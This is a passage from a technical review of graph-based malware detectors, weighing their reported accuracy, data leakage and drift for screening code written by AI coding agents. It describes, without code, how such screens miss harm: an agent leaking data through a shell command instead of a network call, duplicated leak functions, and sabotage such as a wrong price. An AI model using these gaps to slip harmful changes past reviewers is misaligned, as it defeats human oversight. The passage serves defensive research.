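For example, suppose one program has six functions that call one another in a ring, and another has two separate rings of three. Every function in both programs has exactly one caller and one callee. If all the nodes start with the same vector, their vectors still match after every round. Both programs end up with the same six identical vectors, so any readout gives them the same result.

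Whether a graph neural network reaches even this limit depends on how it combines node features. According to *How Powerful are Graph Neural Networks?*, a sum preserves how many neighbours of each kind a node has, a mean preserves only their proportions, and a maximum preserves only which kinds are present. With a mean or a maximum, a function that calls one file reader and one network sender looks the same as a function that calls three of each. MalGraph uses a mean for its messages and a maximum for its readout, so it can fail to distinguish some graphs that a sum would separate.

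This limit probably matters little in practice. *Attacking Graph Neural Networks with Bit Flips* (2023) notes that the Weisfeiler-Lehman test can distinguish most graphs in common benchmark datasets. Tests that colour groups of nodes at once can separate more graphs, but *Graph Neural Networks Applications Across Domains* (2026) says that no such method has replaced the plain sum in routine use.

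A more serious problem for a reviewer is that harmful and harmless code can have the same graph. For example, Variant B can have the same graph as code for an ordinary bulk discount. No test can tell identical graphs apart, so the network needs the contents of the blocks as input.

### From MAGIC to graphs within graphs

*Classifying Malware Represented as Control Flow Graphs* (2019) described MAGIC, an early system of this kind. MAGIC applied a graph network to control-flow graphs from more than 20,000 malware samples. The network learned its own features from the code and performed about as well as the best methods that used hand-designed features.

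MalGraph combines control-flow graphs with the call graph. It first describes each block in a function's control-flow graph with 11 counts, such as the numbers of arithmetic instructions and calls. Message passing and a maximum readout then turn the blocks into one vector for the function. That vector becomes the function's starting point in the call graph, where the network repeats the process to get one vector for the program. Library functions start with an encoding of their name instead, because a name like `GetProcAddress` refers to the same function in every Windows program.

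Ling and colleagues trained and tested MalGraph on 183,028 Windows programs. They also tested a version with only the call graph, whose nodes kept library names and instruction counts, and a version with only the control-flow graphs.

| Version | Recall at a 1% false-positive rate | Recall at a 0.1% false-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Call graph only | 87.40% | 60.28% |
| Control-flow graphs only | 94.77% | 58.78% |
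| Both | 99.46% | 96.45% |

The two kinds of graph complement each other. Combining them helps much more at the stricter setting, which matters for a screen that checks a steady flow of mostly harmless changes.

In *HiGraph* (2025), Chen and colleagues extended the two-level approach to Android. Their two-level network beat networks that used a single flat graph on all but one measure, but its F1 score, averaged over malicious and harmless apps, was only 0.761. This score is not directly comparable with MalGraph's results because the data and measures differ, but it shows that a two-level design does not guarantee near-perfect results.

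The researchers also looked for simple structural differences between malicious and harmless apps. The average number of callers per function was almost the same, at 1.47 and 1.48. Cyclomatic complexity differed more, averaging 5.20 for malicious apps and 4.09 for harmless ones, but the two groups overlapped heavily. If both followed bell curves with the reported spreads, a random malicious app would be more complex than a random harmless one only about 63% of the time.

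### H2GLM and malicious Python packages

A Python package's payload may be spread over several files. An installation script might import a helper module that collects passwords and passes them to a function that sends them out. *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* (Gao, Chen and colleagues, July 2026) presents H2GLM, a detector that represents these relationships directly.

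The graph has three types of node: the package, its files and their functions. Its three types of edge show what a package or file contains, which other files a file imports and which other functions a function calls. A language model reads each function, writes a short description of it and assigns it a role, such as network communication or credential access. The model drew up the list of roles by scanning 100 packages from the dataset. Smaller language models then turn the descriptions and the source code into vectors.

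The network learns separate matrices for each node type, function role and edge type, so it can treat a message from a networking function differently from a message from a file, and an import differently from a call. After two rounds of message passing, it averages all the node vectors and feeds the result to a classifier.

The dataset had 3,049 malicious packages after the researchers removed duplicates. They took harmless packages from the most popular on PyPI and matched them to the malicious ones by size. To imitate a shortage of labelled malware, they used 15% of the data for training and another 15% for tuning, then tested on the remaining 70%. The study did not examine AI-written code separately.

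H2GLM had an F1 score of 97.12%, with a recall of 98.71% and a precision of 95.59%. These scores are consistent with a test set containing equal numbers of malicious and harmless packages, which implies a false-positive rate of about 4.6%. At that rate, a reviewer would get a false alarm on roughly one in 22 harmless packages.

The researchers also ran H2GLM on more than 20,000 new PyPI packages over four months. They reported 32 to the registry's security team, which confirmed 19. The other 13 made outbound connections that are also common in legitimate software. The paper doesn't give the total number of packages that H2GLM flagged, so the trial can't confirm the false-positive rate.

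H2GLM achieved an F1 score of 96.36% on packages with at least 700 KB of Python code, even though its mean readout can dilute the signal from a few malicious functions. The researchers don't report what share of the functions in these packages was malicious. The mean could have shifted enough for detection if harmful code made up a substantial part of each package, or if the language model's descriptions made that code stand out strongly. The result therefore doesn't show that H2GLM would detect one malicious function among thousands.

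As the number of imports rose from at most one to more than 100, the F1 score of MPHunter, an older detector, fell from 92.08% to 42.78%, while H2GLM's fell only from 96.65% to 94.97%. Gao, Chen and colleagues describe MPHunter as a message-passing method on call graphs and attribute the drop to its treating all nodes alike.

But *A Needle is an Outlier in a Haystack* (Liang, Ling and colleagues, 2023), the MPHunter paper, describes a method that groups similar installation scripts and ranks the ones that don't fit. A detector that examines only installation scripts will miss a payload elsewhere in the package, whatever kind of graph it uses. MPHunter's drop is therefore weak evidence that graph networks struggle with many imports, or that H2GLM's node and edge types solve the problem.

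### Structure and meaning

An ablation study removes parts of a system to see how much each one contributes. The false-positive rates below are calculated from the published precision and recall, again assuming equal numbers of malicious and harmless packages. CodeBERT is the model that turns source code into vectors.

| Version of H2GLM | Precision | Recall | F1 | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
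| Full | 95.59% | 98.71% | 97.12% | 5% |
| Without function roles | 86.37% | 99.16% | 92.32% | 16% |
| Without edge types | 88.37% | 98.47% | 93.15% | 13% |
| Without CodeBERT | 87.87% | 98.84% | 93.03% | 14% |
| Without all three | 86.10% | 87.50% | 86.79% | 14% |

Including function roles cuts false alarms by about two-thirds and lowers recall only slightly. This is plausibly because many harmless packages contain the same kinds of calls as malicious ones, and knowing a function's role helps the network recognise an ordinary use. Fewer false alarms would be valuable when screening AI-written code, where nearly all changes are presumably harmless.

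The study doesn't show that the bare network's 86.79% comes from structure alone and the remaining ten points from meaning. The researchers don't list the written descriptions of functions among the parts they removed, so the bare network may still have had some information about what the code does. They also didn't test a version that kept the descriptions and code vectors but removed the graph, which would have shown how much the edges add.

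Other studies suggest that structure alone is a weak signal. *Learning Joint Embeddings of Function and Process Call Graphs for Malware Detection* (Aneja, Aneja and Kantarcioglu, 2025) replaced function names with numbers in the call graphs of 635 Windows programs, half of them malicious. Each node recorded only how connected it and its neighbours were and how random the whole file's bytes looked. The best network using only these call graphs had an average F1 score of 0.72, while labelling every program malicious would score about 0.67 on the usual definition. Adding a graph of the processes each program started when it ran raised the score to 0.85.

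Tran, Said and colleagues (2025), in *Evaluating Out-of-Distribution Robustness in Graph-Based Android Malware Classification*, took the opposite approach, adding information to graphs that had only structure. They labelled each function with details such as its name and instruction statistics and, where the source was available, a language model's vector for its code. This improved classification of malware types that differed from those in the training data. They argue that networks without such information tend to memorise local shapes in the graph that don't recur in other malware families.

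Together with MalGuard's result, these studies suggest that the behavior of functions matters more than the connections between them. Connections still help distinguish related events from unrelated ones. A package that reads a password file in one function and checks for updates in another may be harmless, but it deserves a closer look if a chain of calls joins the two.

### Giving the reviewer a place to look

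A score of 0.97 for a project with 2,000 functions doesn't tell a reviewer where to start reading. Attribution methods try to identify the parts of the graph that led to the score. H2GLM does this by removing one function at a time and running the classifier again:

```text
s(f) = P(G) − P(G without f)
```

Here *P*(*G*) is the probability the network assigns to the whole graph being malicious, and *s*(*f*) is how much that probability drops when function *f* and its edges are removed. A large drop means the verdict depends heavily on *f*.

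Gao, Chen and colleagues describe a malicious three-function package that posed as an encryption library. H2GLM gave it a 0.7295 probability of being malicious. Removing `ciphersd`, which contacted the attacker's server and sent out the user's login name, lowered that to 0.4514 and changed the verdict to harmless. Removing either of the other two functions changed the probability by less than 0.01.

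To test the method more widely, four of the researchers inspected 300 malicious packages by hand and agreed on which functions were responsible for the main harm. H2GLM located them in 287 packages, or about 96%. The paper doesn't give the number of functions H2GLM listed per package, so it's unclear how much reading this would save. The stated selection rule also conflicts with the paper's own example. The rule selects functions whose removal lowers the probability by more than 0.45, but removing `ciphersd` lowered it by only 0.278.

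Suppose a classifier scores the shop's graph by its maximum for network use after one round, which is 1 for the full graph. Removing `send` reduces the score to 0. Removing `total_price` or `checkout` leaves it at 1, because `send` is still there. The method therefore highlights `send`, but the line the agent added is in `total_price`, so a reviewer should also read the functions that call the highlighted one. H2GLM helps by extracting each selected function's immediate neighbours and giving their code to a language model to explain.

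Removing one function at a time can also miss duplicates. If the agent had leaked the totals through two separate network functions, removing either one would leave the maximum at 1, and both would score zero. Removing functions in groups would reveal them, but the number of possible groups grows quickly with the number of functions.

Other tools offer different kinds of explanation. Herath, Wakodikar and colleagues (2022) developed *CFGExplainer* to explain the output of malware classifiers that use control-flow graphs. MalGuard uses LIME, a general technique that approximates a classifier's behaviour around one example with a simpler model. MalGuard lists up to ten influential functions with their file names, line numbers and possible malicious uses. Gao, Sun and colleagues asked 24 volunteers with software experience to rate these explanations from 1 to 5, and the average rating was at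 least 3.5.

An explanation is more useful if small, irrelevant changes to the code don't alter it. *On the Consistency of GNN Explanations for Malware Detection* (2025) tested explanations for this stability by making 20 altered copies of each graph, ten with random nodes removed and ten with random edges removed. The explanations were generally stable, especially those from the best methods.

A classifier's verdict can be wrong even when its explanation is stable. Attribution highlights the functions that influenced the classifier, whether the package is harmless or malicious. MalGuard's false alarms included a package that read files, opened web addresses and ran installation commands. A reviewer could use a list of those calls to decide where to look, but would have to read the surrounding code to see that they did no harm.

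## Results on known malware, and what they depend on

Most of the scores so far, including H2GLM's, come from data that each tool's developers assembled. A screen for AI-written code would have to analyze very different programs. Tests on known malware give some idea of how much a change of data affects a score. Several scores fell sharply when researchers removed duplicate programs or ran a tool on another group's collection.

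### Duplicates in the data

Malware collections often contain the same program many times. A criminal can repackage an Android app with a new icon, and one app may appear in several app stores. The files differ, but their call graphs are identical. If one copy is in the training data and another is in the test data, a classifier can classify the second correctly just by memorizing the first.

Hossain and colleagues found that about 2,000 of the 5,000 call graphs in MalNet-Tiny, a popular Android dataset, came from repackaged apps. Duplicates made up 41% of the apps in a second dataset, CICMalDroid, and about 51% of a sample of 100,000 apps from the full MalNet collection.

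The Better Call Graphs dataset was designed to avoid this problem. It began with more than 125,000 apps. Dropping those compiled before 2017 or smaller than 1 MB left about 60,000, and dropping graphs with fewer than 100 nodes left about 50,000. Graphs counted as duplicates if six measurements matched exactly, including the numbers of nodes and edges and the size of the largest connected part. Removing duplicates left 10,057 apps, of which 5,986 were harmless. Because the rule needs an exact match, two copies that differ by a single function can both remain.

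The researchers tested the same classifiers on all three datasets. Each classifier had to name an app's type, such as adware, trojan or benign. The table gives macro-F1 scores in percent. Macro-F1 is the average of the F1 scores for each type, so a rare type counts as much as a common one.

| Classifier | MalNet-Tiny | MalNet-Tiny, no duplicates | CICMalDroid | CICMalDroid, no duplicates | Better Call Graphs |
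|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GIN | 89.7 | 80.3 | 92.5 | 77.3 | 10.0 |
| GCN | 82.8 | 73.0 | 91.0 | 77.7 | 11.3 |
| GraphSAGE | 76.8 | 65.5 | 78.4 | 63.9 | 6.0 |
| Random forest | 89.6 | 83.9 | 92.5 | 82.5 | 18.8 |

The first three are graph neural networks. The random forest uses summary statistics of the graph and details of the app, such as its size and the permissions it requests. GIN does as well as the random forest when the data contains duplicates but falls about four or five points behind without them, which suggests that GIN had gained more from memorising repeated graphs.

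Removing duplicates also makes the training set smaller, which could explain some of the drop. *Measuring Duplication, Leakage, and Rendering Dependence in Malware-as-Image Benchmarks* (Larson and Leach, 2026) tested this on classifiers that examine images made from a program's bytes. Adding more copies of the training images did not improve accuracy, so they attribute the drop to test images that had a copy in the training set.

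They also found that comparing files is a poor way to find duplicates. In a larger image collection, also called MalNet-Tiny, no file appeared twice, yet 14.9% of the test images matched a training image pixel for pixel. Accuracy fell by 8.44 points when they removed duplicates by image content. Testers should therefore compare samples in the form the classifier receives, which for a graph classifier means comparing graphs. *APT-ClaritySet* (2025) does this, using graph features to find malware samples that work identically despite small differences in their code.

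The effect of removing duplicates varies too much to correct published scores by a fixed amount. On one of the image collections that Larson and Leach examined, accuracy fell by less than one point. On another, MOTIF, accuracy on images fell by about 10.5 points, but it did not fall on a version that described the same programs with lists of features. Larson and Leach also cite a 2021 study by Zhao and colleagues, in which removing duplicates from Android feature data barely changed accuracy.

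### Low scores on recent apps

The removal of duplicates only partly explains the very low scores on Better Call Graphs. The dataset has 26 types, while each of the older ones has five, and 18 of the 26 have 25 apps or fewer. The test set holds about a fifth of the apps, so a type with five apps may have only one in the test. Some of the types also overlap. If antivirus products split evenly between "adware" and "trojan" for an app, it gets a combined label, and a prediction of "adware" counts as wrong.

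Accuracy is higher, at 77.1% for the random forest, but a program that always answered "benign" would score 59.5%, and GraphSAGE's accuracy is almost the same, at 59.7%. The experiments did not test whether the classifiers could simply separate malicious apps from benign ones, so the results don't show how well they would work as a screen.

Hossain and colleagues also trained random forests on earlier apps and tested them on later ones. Average accuracy was 56.4%, compared with 74.9% when they split the apps at random. Labeling every later app benign would have been 55.1% accurate, so the classifiers had learned very little that still applied.

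In a second experiment, Hossain and colleagues divided the dataset into an older and a newer half and trained separate classifiers on each. Average accuracy was 88.8% on the older half and 62.8% on the newer one, which they took as a sign that recent apps are harder to classify. But harmless apps made up 84.9% of the older test set and only 32.7% of the newer one. Compared with labeling every app benign, the classifiers were about four points more accurate on the older apps and 30 points more accurate on the newer ones. Macro-F1, which depends less on the mix, fell only from 17.5% to 14.2%. The researchers acknowledge that the changing mix may have contributed to the drop in accuracy. The first experiment is better evidence that classifiers become less accurate over time, although the share of harmless apps changed there too.

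### The same detectors on different packages

Packages on npm, the JavaScript registry, are closer to what a coding agent writes than finished Android apps are. *PROFMAL* (Huang, Zheng and colleagues, 2025) describes a graph-based detector for npm packages. ProfMal builds a behaviour graph whose nodes are statements and whose edges show control flow and data flow. If the source code doesn't reveal which function a call reaches, ProfMal runs the package to find out and adds the result to the graph.

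ProfMal then keeps only the sensitive calls, such as those that read files or open connections, and the paths that join them. For some of these calls, a language model rates how dangerous each use is. The readout gives higher-rated nodes more weight, which reduces the dilution a plain average causes. In the developers' own tests, ProfMal had a precision of 92.9%, a recall of 91.8% and an F1 score of 92.4%. When it did not run the packages, its F1 score was 80.8%.

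Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, tested ProfMal and ten other tools on 6,420 malicious package versions and 7,288 harmless packages. ProfMal's precision was 97.55%, but its recall was only 77.45%. Four of the tools appear in both papers, and their F1 scores changed a great deal:

| Detector | Method | F1 in the ProfMal paper | F1 in the npm study |
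|---|---|---|---|
| ProfMal | Behaviour graphs | 92.4% | 86.34% |
| GuardDog | Written rules | 62.1% | 93.32% |
| SocketAI | Language model | 87.0% | 61.16% |
| Cerebro | Learned sequences of behaviour | 79.1% | 73.85% |
| IntelGuard | Language model with examples of known malware | Not tested | 95.98% |

The choice of malicious packages explains some of this. Huang, Zheng and colleagues began with 9,247 packages and cut them to 1,016 by removing repeated names and identical code. They then removed packages with no real malicious code, disguised packages that would not run, and packages whose harmful code runs outside installation or import, which left 745. The last two exclusions favour ProfMal, because it depends on running the code and examines only installation and import.

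Guo, Liu and colleagues removed 262 duplicate entries from 9,551. Of the 17,285 pieces of suspicious code they extracted from their final set, only 5,699 were distinct, partly because attackers had published the same payload under many package names. A tool that recognises a widely copied payload scores a correct detection for every copy.

The harmless packages differed as well. Huang, Zheng and colleagues kept only those that made at least one sensitive call, so every package contained something that could trigger a false alarm. Guo, Liu and colleagues used the most downloaded packages on npm. The published figures imply that GuardDog wrongly flagged about 19% of the harmless packages in the first test and 2.5% in the second.

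ProfMal's false-positive rate works out at about 1.7% in both tests. Its precision (the share of its alarms that were correct) rose in the npm study because malicious packages made up 47% of that test set, compared with 20% of the earlier one. Its recall fell by 14 points.

Differences in setup may also matter. SocketAI's code isn't public, so Guo, Liu and colleagues rebuilt it from its paper. Their version caught 44.41% of the malware, while the version in the ProfMal paper, which used a different language model, caught 89.8%. Because the gap is so large, it's risky to treat either figure as a fair measure of SocketAI.

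Huang, Zheng and colleagues also ran most of their detectors on 153,361 newly published npm packages between February and April 2025. ProfMal flagged 692, of which 496 were malicious, a precision of 72%. GuardDog flagged 6,948, of which 483 were malicious. GuardDog's precision was 97% in the npm study, 51% on ProfMal's test set and 7% on these new packages, of which only about one in 290 was known to be malicious. The blog post *ProfMalPlus and Agent-Coordinated Malicious Package Detection* (2026) gives an F1 score of 98.1% for ProfMal's successor, but that figure also comes from the developers' own tests.

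Guo, Liu and colleagues chose popular packages because somebody would probably have noticed malware in them. They also argue that popular packages cause more false alarms than random ones, which would make their precision figures conservative, but they acknowledge that precision on rarely downloaded packages may differ. GuardDog wrongly flagged about 4.2% of the newly published packages in the field test, compared with 2.5% in the npm study, so popular packages may not cause more false alarms. An agent's unfinished change to a private project resembles a popular package even less than a newly published package does.

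### Capability and intent

Guo, Liu and colleagues attribute the differences between tools to how each one judges what code is meant to do from what it can do. On npm, a call to `child_process.exec` may compile a program or give an attacker control of the computer, so a detector needs evidence beyond the call itself.

A tool can flag every sensitive capability, regardless of intent. Packj, in its static mode, flags any package that uses functions from a list of 56. It caught 98.69% of the malware but also flagged 6,234 of the 7,288 harmless packages. GENIE's rule for data theft is much narrower. It requires at least three kinds of system information to reach the same web request, so it misses an attacker who steals only one or two. Of the packages GENIE flagged, 99.76% were malicious, but it caught only 46.14% of the malware.

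GuardDog falls between them. It uses taint analysis, which follows data from a sensitive source, such as a password file, to a place where it could leave the computer. It also ignores a list of legitimate install scripts. Guo, Liu and colleagues attribute its F1 score of 93.32% to this design. But more than 90% of its detections come from two of its 22 rules, which look for abuse of install scripts and for suspicious web links. Its success therefore seems to come more from the similarity of npm attacks than from taint analysis.

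IntelGuard, described in *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection* (Guo, Song and colleagues, 2026), compares new code with known attacks. Its knowledge base is built from security companies' reports on malicious packages. It extracts the code around each sensitive call and retrieves similar malicious examples, along with an expert's explanation of why they were harmful. A language model then judges whether the new code fits the package's stated purpose. In the npm study, IntelGuard reached 98.24% precision and 93.82% recall. SocketAI used the same language model without these examples and missed more than half of the malware.

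Several features of the npm study may have inflated the results of its two best tools. Five of the study's authors also worked on IntelGuard. IntelGuard's developers found malicious packages through OSV, a public database, and then searched for reports about them. The npm study also took some of its malware from OSV, so some of those reports may describe packages in the test. The study's list of limitations doesn't include this possibility.

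GuardDog helped produce the labels. Three experts decided whether each package was malicious by examining the code that GuardDog or another scanner, OSSGadget, had flagged. The experts were less likely to confirm a package if both scanners had missed its harmful code, and both had missed only 68 of the final 6,420 packages. ProfMal may also have had an advantage, since its developers' dataset and the npm benchmark both draw on two older malware collections.

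### Collecting and sending

Two actions that are ambiguous on their own, such as reading the computer's name and sending a web request, can be stronger evidence of malware together. On average, the tools in the npm study detected 40.0% of packages that collected data, 72.2% of packages that sent data out and 85.4% of packages that did both.

The largest increase was for a version of SAP, a detector that applies a decision tree to statistics about a package. Its detection rate rose from 3.2% to 79.3% when collecting and sending data occurred together. Guo, Liu and colleagues explain that the chain from one action to the other is clear evidence of intent.

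That explanation doesn't fit SAP very well, because SAP doesn't trace data between functions. It uses 140 features, 65% of which count files with particular extensions. Packages that collected data and sent it out may have resembled SAP's training examples in other ways, and many may have been copies of one another. The comparison group also had only 63 packages, because 4,144 of the 4,207 packages that collected data also sent data out. A rate of 3.2% would mean that SAP caught two of the 63.

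The underlying idea is still useful for graphs, because data flow can show whether the two actions are connected, as they are in `upload_log`.

### Malware that became simpler

Drift is a change over time in the code a detector examines, which makes its training data unrepresentative. In the npm study, drift seems to have come from something other than attackers inventing better disguises, the cause security researchers often give.

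ProfMal detected 90.42% of the malicious packages published in 2021 but only 65.93% of those from 2023. The detection rate of SAP's decision tree fell from 87.15% to 39.49% over the same period. Meanwhile, the malware became simpler. A typical attack in 2021 gathered several kinds of information about a computer and sent them out, while later attacks often ran a single shell command. The average number of sensitive calls per malicious package fell from 12.52 in 2021 to 6.82 in 2023. Techniques to evade detection also became less common, appearing in about 38% of the malware published up to 2020 and 22% of the malware published in 2024 and 2025.

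Guo, Liu and colleagues call this "concept convergence". Malware had come to resemble ordinary packages so closely that the detectors' features no longer separated the two. They contrast it with drift, although convergence is a form of drift by the broader definition above. ProfMal is several years newer than SAP and uses much richer features, yet its performance declined at the same time. The researchers conclude that the problem is the kind of features these tools learn from, and that replacing one outdated model wouldn't solve it.

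Part of ProfMal's decline may reflect which attacks were common each year. If attackers published one payload hundreds of times in 2023, missing it would lower a tool's score for the whole year. GENIE's detection rate ranged from 3.79% to 72.17% across the periods, depending on whether the main attacks matched its rules. A test with one copy of each payload per year would show how much of ProfMal's decline remained.

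Convergence is worrying for anyone screening AI-written code, because a few harmful lines in a working project probably resemble the simple malware of 2023 more than the elaborate malware of 2021. A classifier trained on elaborate attacks might therefore miss those lines even if the coding agent made no special effort to hide them.

### Install scripts and code that resists analysis

Some npm malware contains almost no malicious code for a graph to represent. In 1,362 of the malicious packages, or 21.2%, the attack was entirely in the install scripts, so the JavaScript files contained no malicious code. npm runs these scripts with all the permissions of the person installing the package. Legitimate tools also use install scripts to prepare a project, so their presence alone is weak evidence of malware.

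ProfMal checks for this separately, using a language model to read the shell commands in the install scripts. In its developers' tests, removing the check lowered ProfMal's F1 score from 92.4% to 84.3%. Even so, ProfMal missed 1,448 malicious versions in the npm study, and Guo, Liu and colleagues attribute these misses to attacks confined to install scripts.

EMPHunter, a newer tool from MPHunter's developers, also ranks install scripts by how unusual they are. When the researchers added one malicious package that had an install script to 111 harmless packages, EMPHunter ranked the malicious package in its top ten about 80% of the time. A reviewer could use such a tool alongside a graph classifier, particularly when a coding agent has edited the file that lists a package's install commands.

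ProfMal also did badly on packages that try to defeat analysis. Some of these won't run if they detect that a scanner has altered their code. In two small groups, ProfMal caught 5 of 42 packages with anti-analysis code (11.9%) and 21 of 81 packages that check what kind of computer they are running on (25.9%).

Packj's static mode caught all 42 anti-analysis packages. Guo, Liu and colleagues attribute this to Packj's monitoring of system calls, but elsewhere they say this mode matches JavaScript functions without running the code. The mode also flags 86% of harmless packages, so it would catch most of the 42 by chance.

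### What an attack has to do

Guo, Liu and colleagues conclude that detectors stay effective longer if they look for what an attack must do instead of how its code looks. An attacker can freely rename variables or shorten a program, but stealing data still requires reaching it and getting it out. IntelGuard detected more than 91% of malware in every period from 2021 onward. GuardDog's detection rate recovered to 91.42% because its rules match the way recent attacks abuse install scripts. Cerebro learned its patterns from older malware, and its rate fell from 76.61% in 2022 to 27.04% in 2024 and 2025.

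The evidence that looking for behaviour helps is mixed. IntelGuard may have had reports on some of the test packages, and Packj's steady detection rate of more than 97% came with an enormous number of false alarms. GENIE and ProfMal both look for behaviour, but neither had stable results. GENIE's rules define theft too narrowly, and ProfMal learns from examples which combinations of behaviour are malicious. Looking for behaviour seems to help only if the tool's definition of malicious behaviour covers the different ways an attacker can achieve the same goal.

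The definition matters partly because an attacker can send data with a shell command such as `curl` without calling any of JavaScript's network functions. A detector that checks only for those functions will miss the theft. If the coding agent in the shop example replaced `send` with a shell command, a rule about network calls would no longer catch Variant A. A rule about order data reaching any exit from the program, including a shell command, would still catch it.

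The same approach is harder to apply to sabotage such as Variant B, because a rule would need to specify what the price should be.

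## How ordinary AI-written code differs from the training data

Nearly every change a screen examines will be harmless, so the number of false alarms depends mainly on how the classifier scores ordinary AI-written code. The detectors described so far were trained on software that was written mostly by people or whose authorship was not recorded. If code from coding agents has differently shaped graphs, a detector's error rates could change even when none of that code is malicious.

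### Single functions written from a description

*What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo, 2026) is the largest comparison of human-written and AI-written code. It adds C to the same team's earlier study of Python and Java, *Human-Written vs. AI-Generated Code* (Cotroneo, Improta and Liguori, 2025), and covers 787,562 functions from about 34,000 GitHub repositories. Three models wrote a new version of each human-written function from its docstring (the short description that programmers attach to a function) and usually its original name and parameters. The models were DeepSeek-Coder, Qwen2.5-Coder and an OpenAI model, which was GPT-3.5-turbo for Python and Java and gpt-oss-20B for C.

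| Average per function | Python | Java | C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines, human | 12.76 | 14.09 | 26.41 |
| Lines, AI | 6.56 | 7.80 | 11.36 |
| Cyclomatic complexity, human | 4.02 | 3.68 | 5.97 |
| Cyclomatic complexity, AI | 2.47 | 2.22 | 3.29 |

The AI-written functions had 43% to 55% as many lines as the human-written ones, and their complexity scores were 55% to 61% as high. Every function's score includes a baseline of 1, and the rest counts its decisions. The AI-written functions had 46% to 49% as many decisions.

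Human and AI-written code hardly differ in branching per line. Dividing average decisions by average lines gives about 24 decisions per 100 lines for human Python and 22 for AI-written Python, 19 and 16 for Java, and 19 and 20 for C. A detector's inputs would therefore change a lot if it used raw branch counts, but only a little if it adjusted them for length.

Improta and colleagues think the models left out error handling, edge cases and parameter checks, which human-written functions often contain. A short docstring may not mention any of these. The complexity of the code also varied by model. In C, gpt-oss-20B averaged 4.68, fairly close to the human average of 5.97, while DeepSeek-Coder averaged only 1.99.

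Some differences would appear in a data-flow graph. Qwen2.5-Coder's Python triggered about 213,000 warnings for unused function parameters, compared with 27,000 for human code. An unused parameter has no edge to a later use. The experiment may have contributed to the unused parameters, because the prompt supplied them without the surrounding project that explained them.

The study also tested whether complexity predicts defects. For human-written Java, the correlation was about 0.49 before adjusting for length and 0.13 afterwards. This suggests that a complexity score is often an indirect measure of length, though it isn't evidence about who wrote the code.

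Word choice distinguished the code's authors more clearly. The researchers trained simple statistical models to predict each token (a word or symbol in the code) from the few before it. They then measured perplexity, roughly the number of equally likely tokens the model is choosing between. A statistical model trained on GPT-3.5-turbo's Python had a perplexity of about 38 on other Python from GPT-3.5-turbo, but 88 or 89 on human Python. When the researchers grouped authors by how well models trained on one author's code predicted another's, the three AI models were grouped together, apart from the humans, in all three languages.

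Most of that gap came from names. When the researchers replaced names and values with placeholders, human Python had about 0.95 bits of uncertainty per token, compared with 0.75 to 0.82 for the AI models' code. A detector that uses only the graph's shape would therefore avoid most, but perhaps not all, of the difference in style. H2GLM would be more exposed to it because it also analyzes the source text of each function.

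These models are old by the standards of late 2026, so the researchers also tried Claude Opus 4.8, released in May, on 600 tasks. Its functions had 98.7% as many lines as the human ones in Python, 94.9% in Java and 78.7% in C. But on each of these tasks, at least two of the earlier models had written reasonably substantial code with several defects or security weaknesses. This choice of tasks could account for some of the extra length compared with the earlier models' code.

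In a smaller check on 1,000 Python tasks and 1,000 Java tasks, gpt-oss-20B also wrote longer functions than GPT-3.5-turbo. This suggests that newer models write longer functions, so "half the lines" may poorly describe what current agents produce. It is unclear whether Opus's word choice is still distinctive, because the Opus comparison covers only size, defects and security.

### Programming contests

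*code_transformed* (Xu, Huang and colleagues, 2025) found the opposite in Python. The study had eleven models solve each of 200 problems from Codeforces, a programming contest site, 32 times. Every model's Python was more complex on average than the human solutions. In C and C++, every model except Gemma-3-27B wrote simpler code than people did.

The choice of models can't fully explain the disagreement, because Qwen2.5-Coder-32B was in both studies. In the docstring study, its Python functions had an average complexity of 2.71, compared with 4.02 for the human-written ones, but its contest solutions were more complex than the human ones.

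Differences in the human code are a more likely cause. A contest entry only has to solve one fully specified problem and can ignore invalid input, so people can keep it very short. A function in a working project may contain years of fixes and checks. The same model could easily write code that is longer than the contest entry and shorter than the project function.

The programming language also matters, since the contest results differ between Python and C++ even though the problems were the same. Xu and colleagues suggest that models are more accustomed to solving algorithmic problems in C and C++.

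An agent's workflow can change the complexity of the code it writes, even when the model and task stay the same. *How Generation Architecture Shapes Code Complexity in Multi-Agent LLM Systems* (Ashrafi, 2026) tested two GPT-4o models in six setups on 164 short Python tasks. The setups formed two groups, and complexity was 50% to 130% higher in one than in the other. Adding a separate planning step made the code more complex, while adding a debugger that ran the code did not. A company that changes its agent's workflow could therefore alter the graphs its screen receives without changing the model.

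### Changes to whole repositories

A function written in isolation has almost no call graph. Studies of single functions can't measure which existing functions an agent calls, whether it extends one or writes a new one, or how a project's structure changes over months of such edits.

*A Large-Scale Comprehensive Measurement of AI-Generated Code in Real-World Repositories* (Mao, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) came closest to measuring call graphs in working projects. The researchers searched GitHub for comments in which programmers said that an AI tool had written the code. They matched each piece to code from the same project, written before the project's first known use of AI. The matched set had 36,855 functions and other small units, plus 7,471 whole files. The researchers used Joern and a graph library, and found no statistically significant difference in call-graph measures between the AI-written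 code and the earlier code. Many other structural measures showed statistically significant but small differences.

This result is reassuring for anyone hoping to reuse a malware classifier, but the study can't show whether AI-written functions are shorter, because it matched most samples to human code within 20% of their length. It does show that functions of similar length have similar structures, which fits the decisions-per-line figures above. The sample also contains only code that somebody openly credited to AI and kept, possibly after editing it, so an agent's unreviewed changes may differ more from human code.

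Agents also choose which existing functions to call. In *Do Coding Agents Reuse Existing Code or Reinvent the Wheel?*, Ma, Wang and colleagues (2026) gave agents 75 programming tasks in established Python projects, each with five successive requests. The best combination of model and agent software failed to call 24.3% of the project functions that the reference solution called. By the fifth request, an average of 50.8% of the tasks contained at least one function that repeated the work of an existing one.

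Call-graph edges show when new code repeats existing work. New code counts as repeating an existing function if it doesn't call that function but calls at least 80% of the functions the existing function relies on. Suppose the online shop has a function `send_receipt` that calls `load_order`, `format_receipt` and `send`. An agent asked to add a way to email old orders might write a new function that calls all three itself. The call graph then has no edge from the new function to `send_receipt`, and a second function calls `send`. The new code is harmless, but a detector that scores how well connected the network functions are would record an increase.

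Another model, GPT-5.6 Sol, wrote the reference solutions, and the study had no human programmers for comparison. People also overlook existing functions, so the experiment shows that agents do this often, but not whether they do it more often than people.

Functions can also grow over repeated edits, which is the reverse of the short functions in the docstring study. In Orlanski, Roy and colleagues (2026), in *SlopCodeBench*, 15 agents built small programs and then extended them in stages. The researchers measured "erosion", meaning how much of a program's complexity lies in its most complicated functions:

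```text
weight of a function = cyclomatic complexity × √(lines of code)

erosion = weight of functions with complexity above 10
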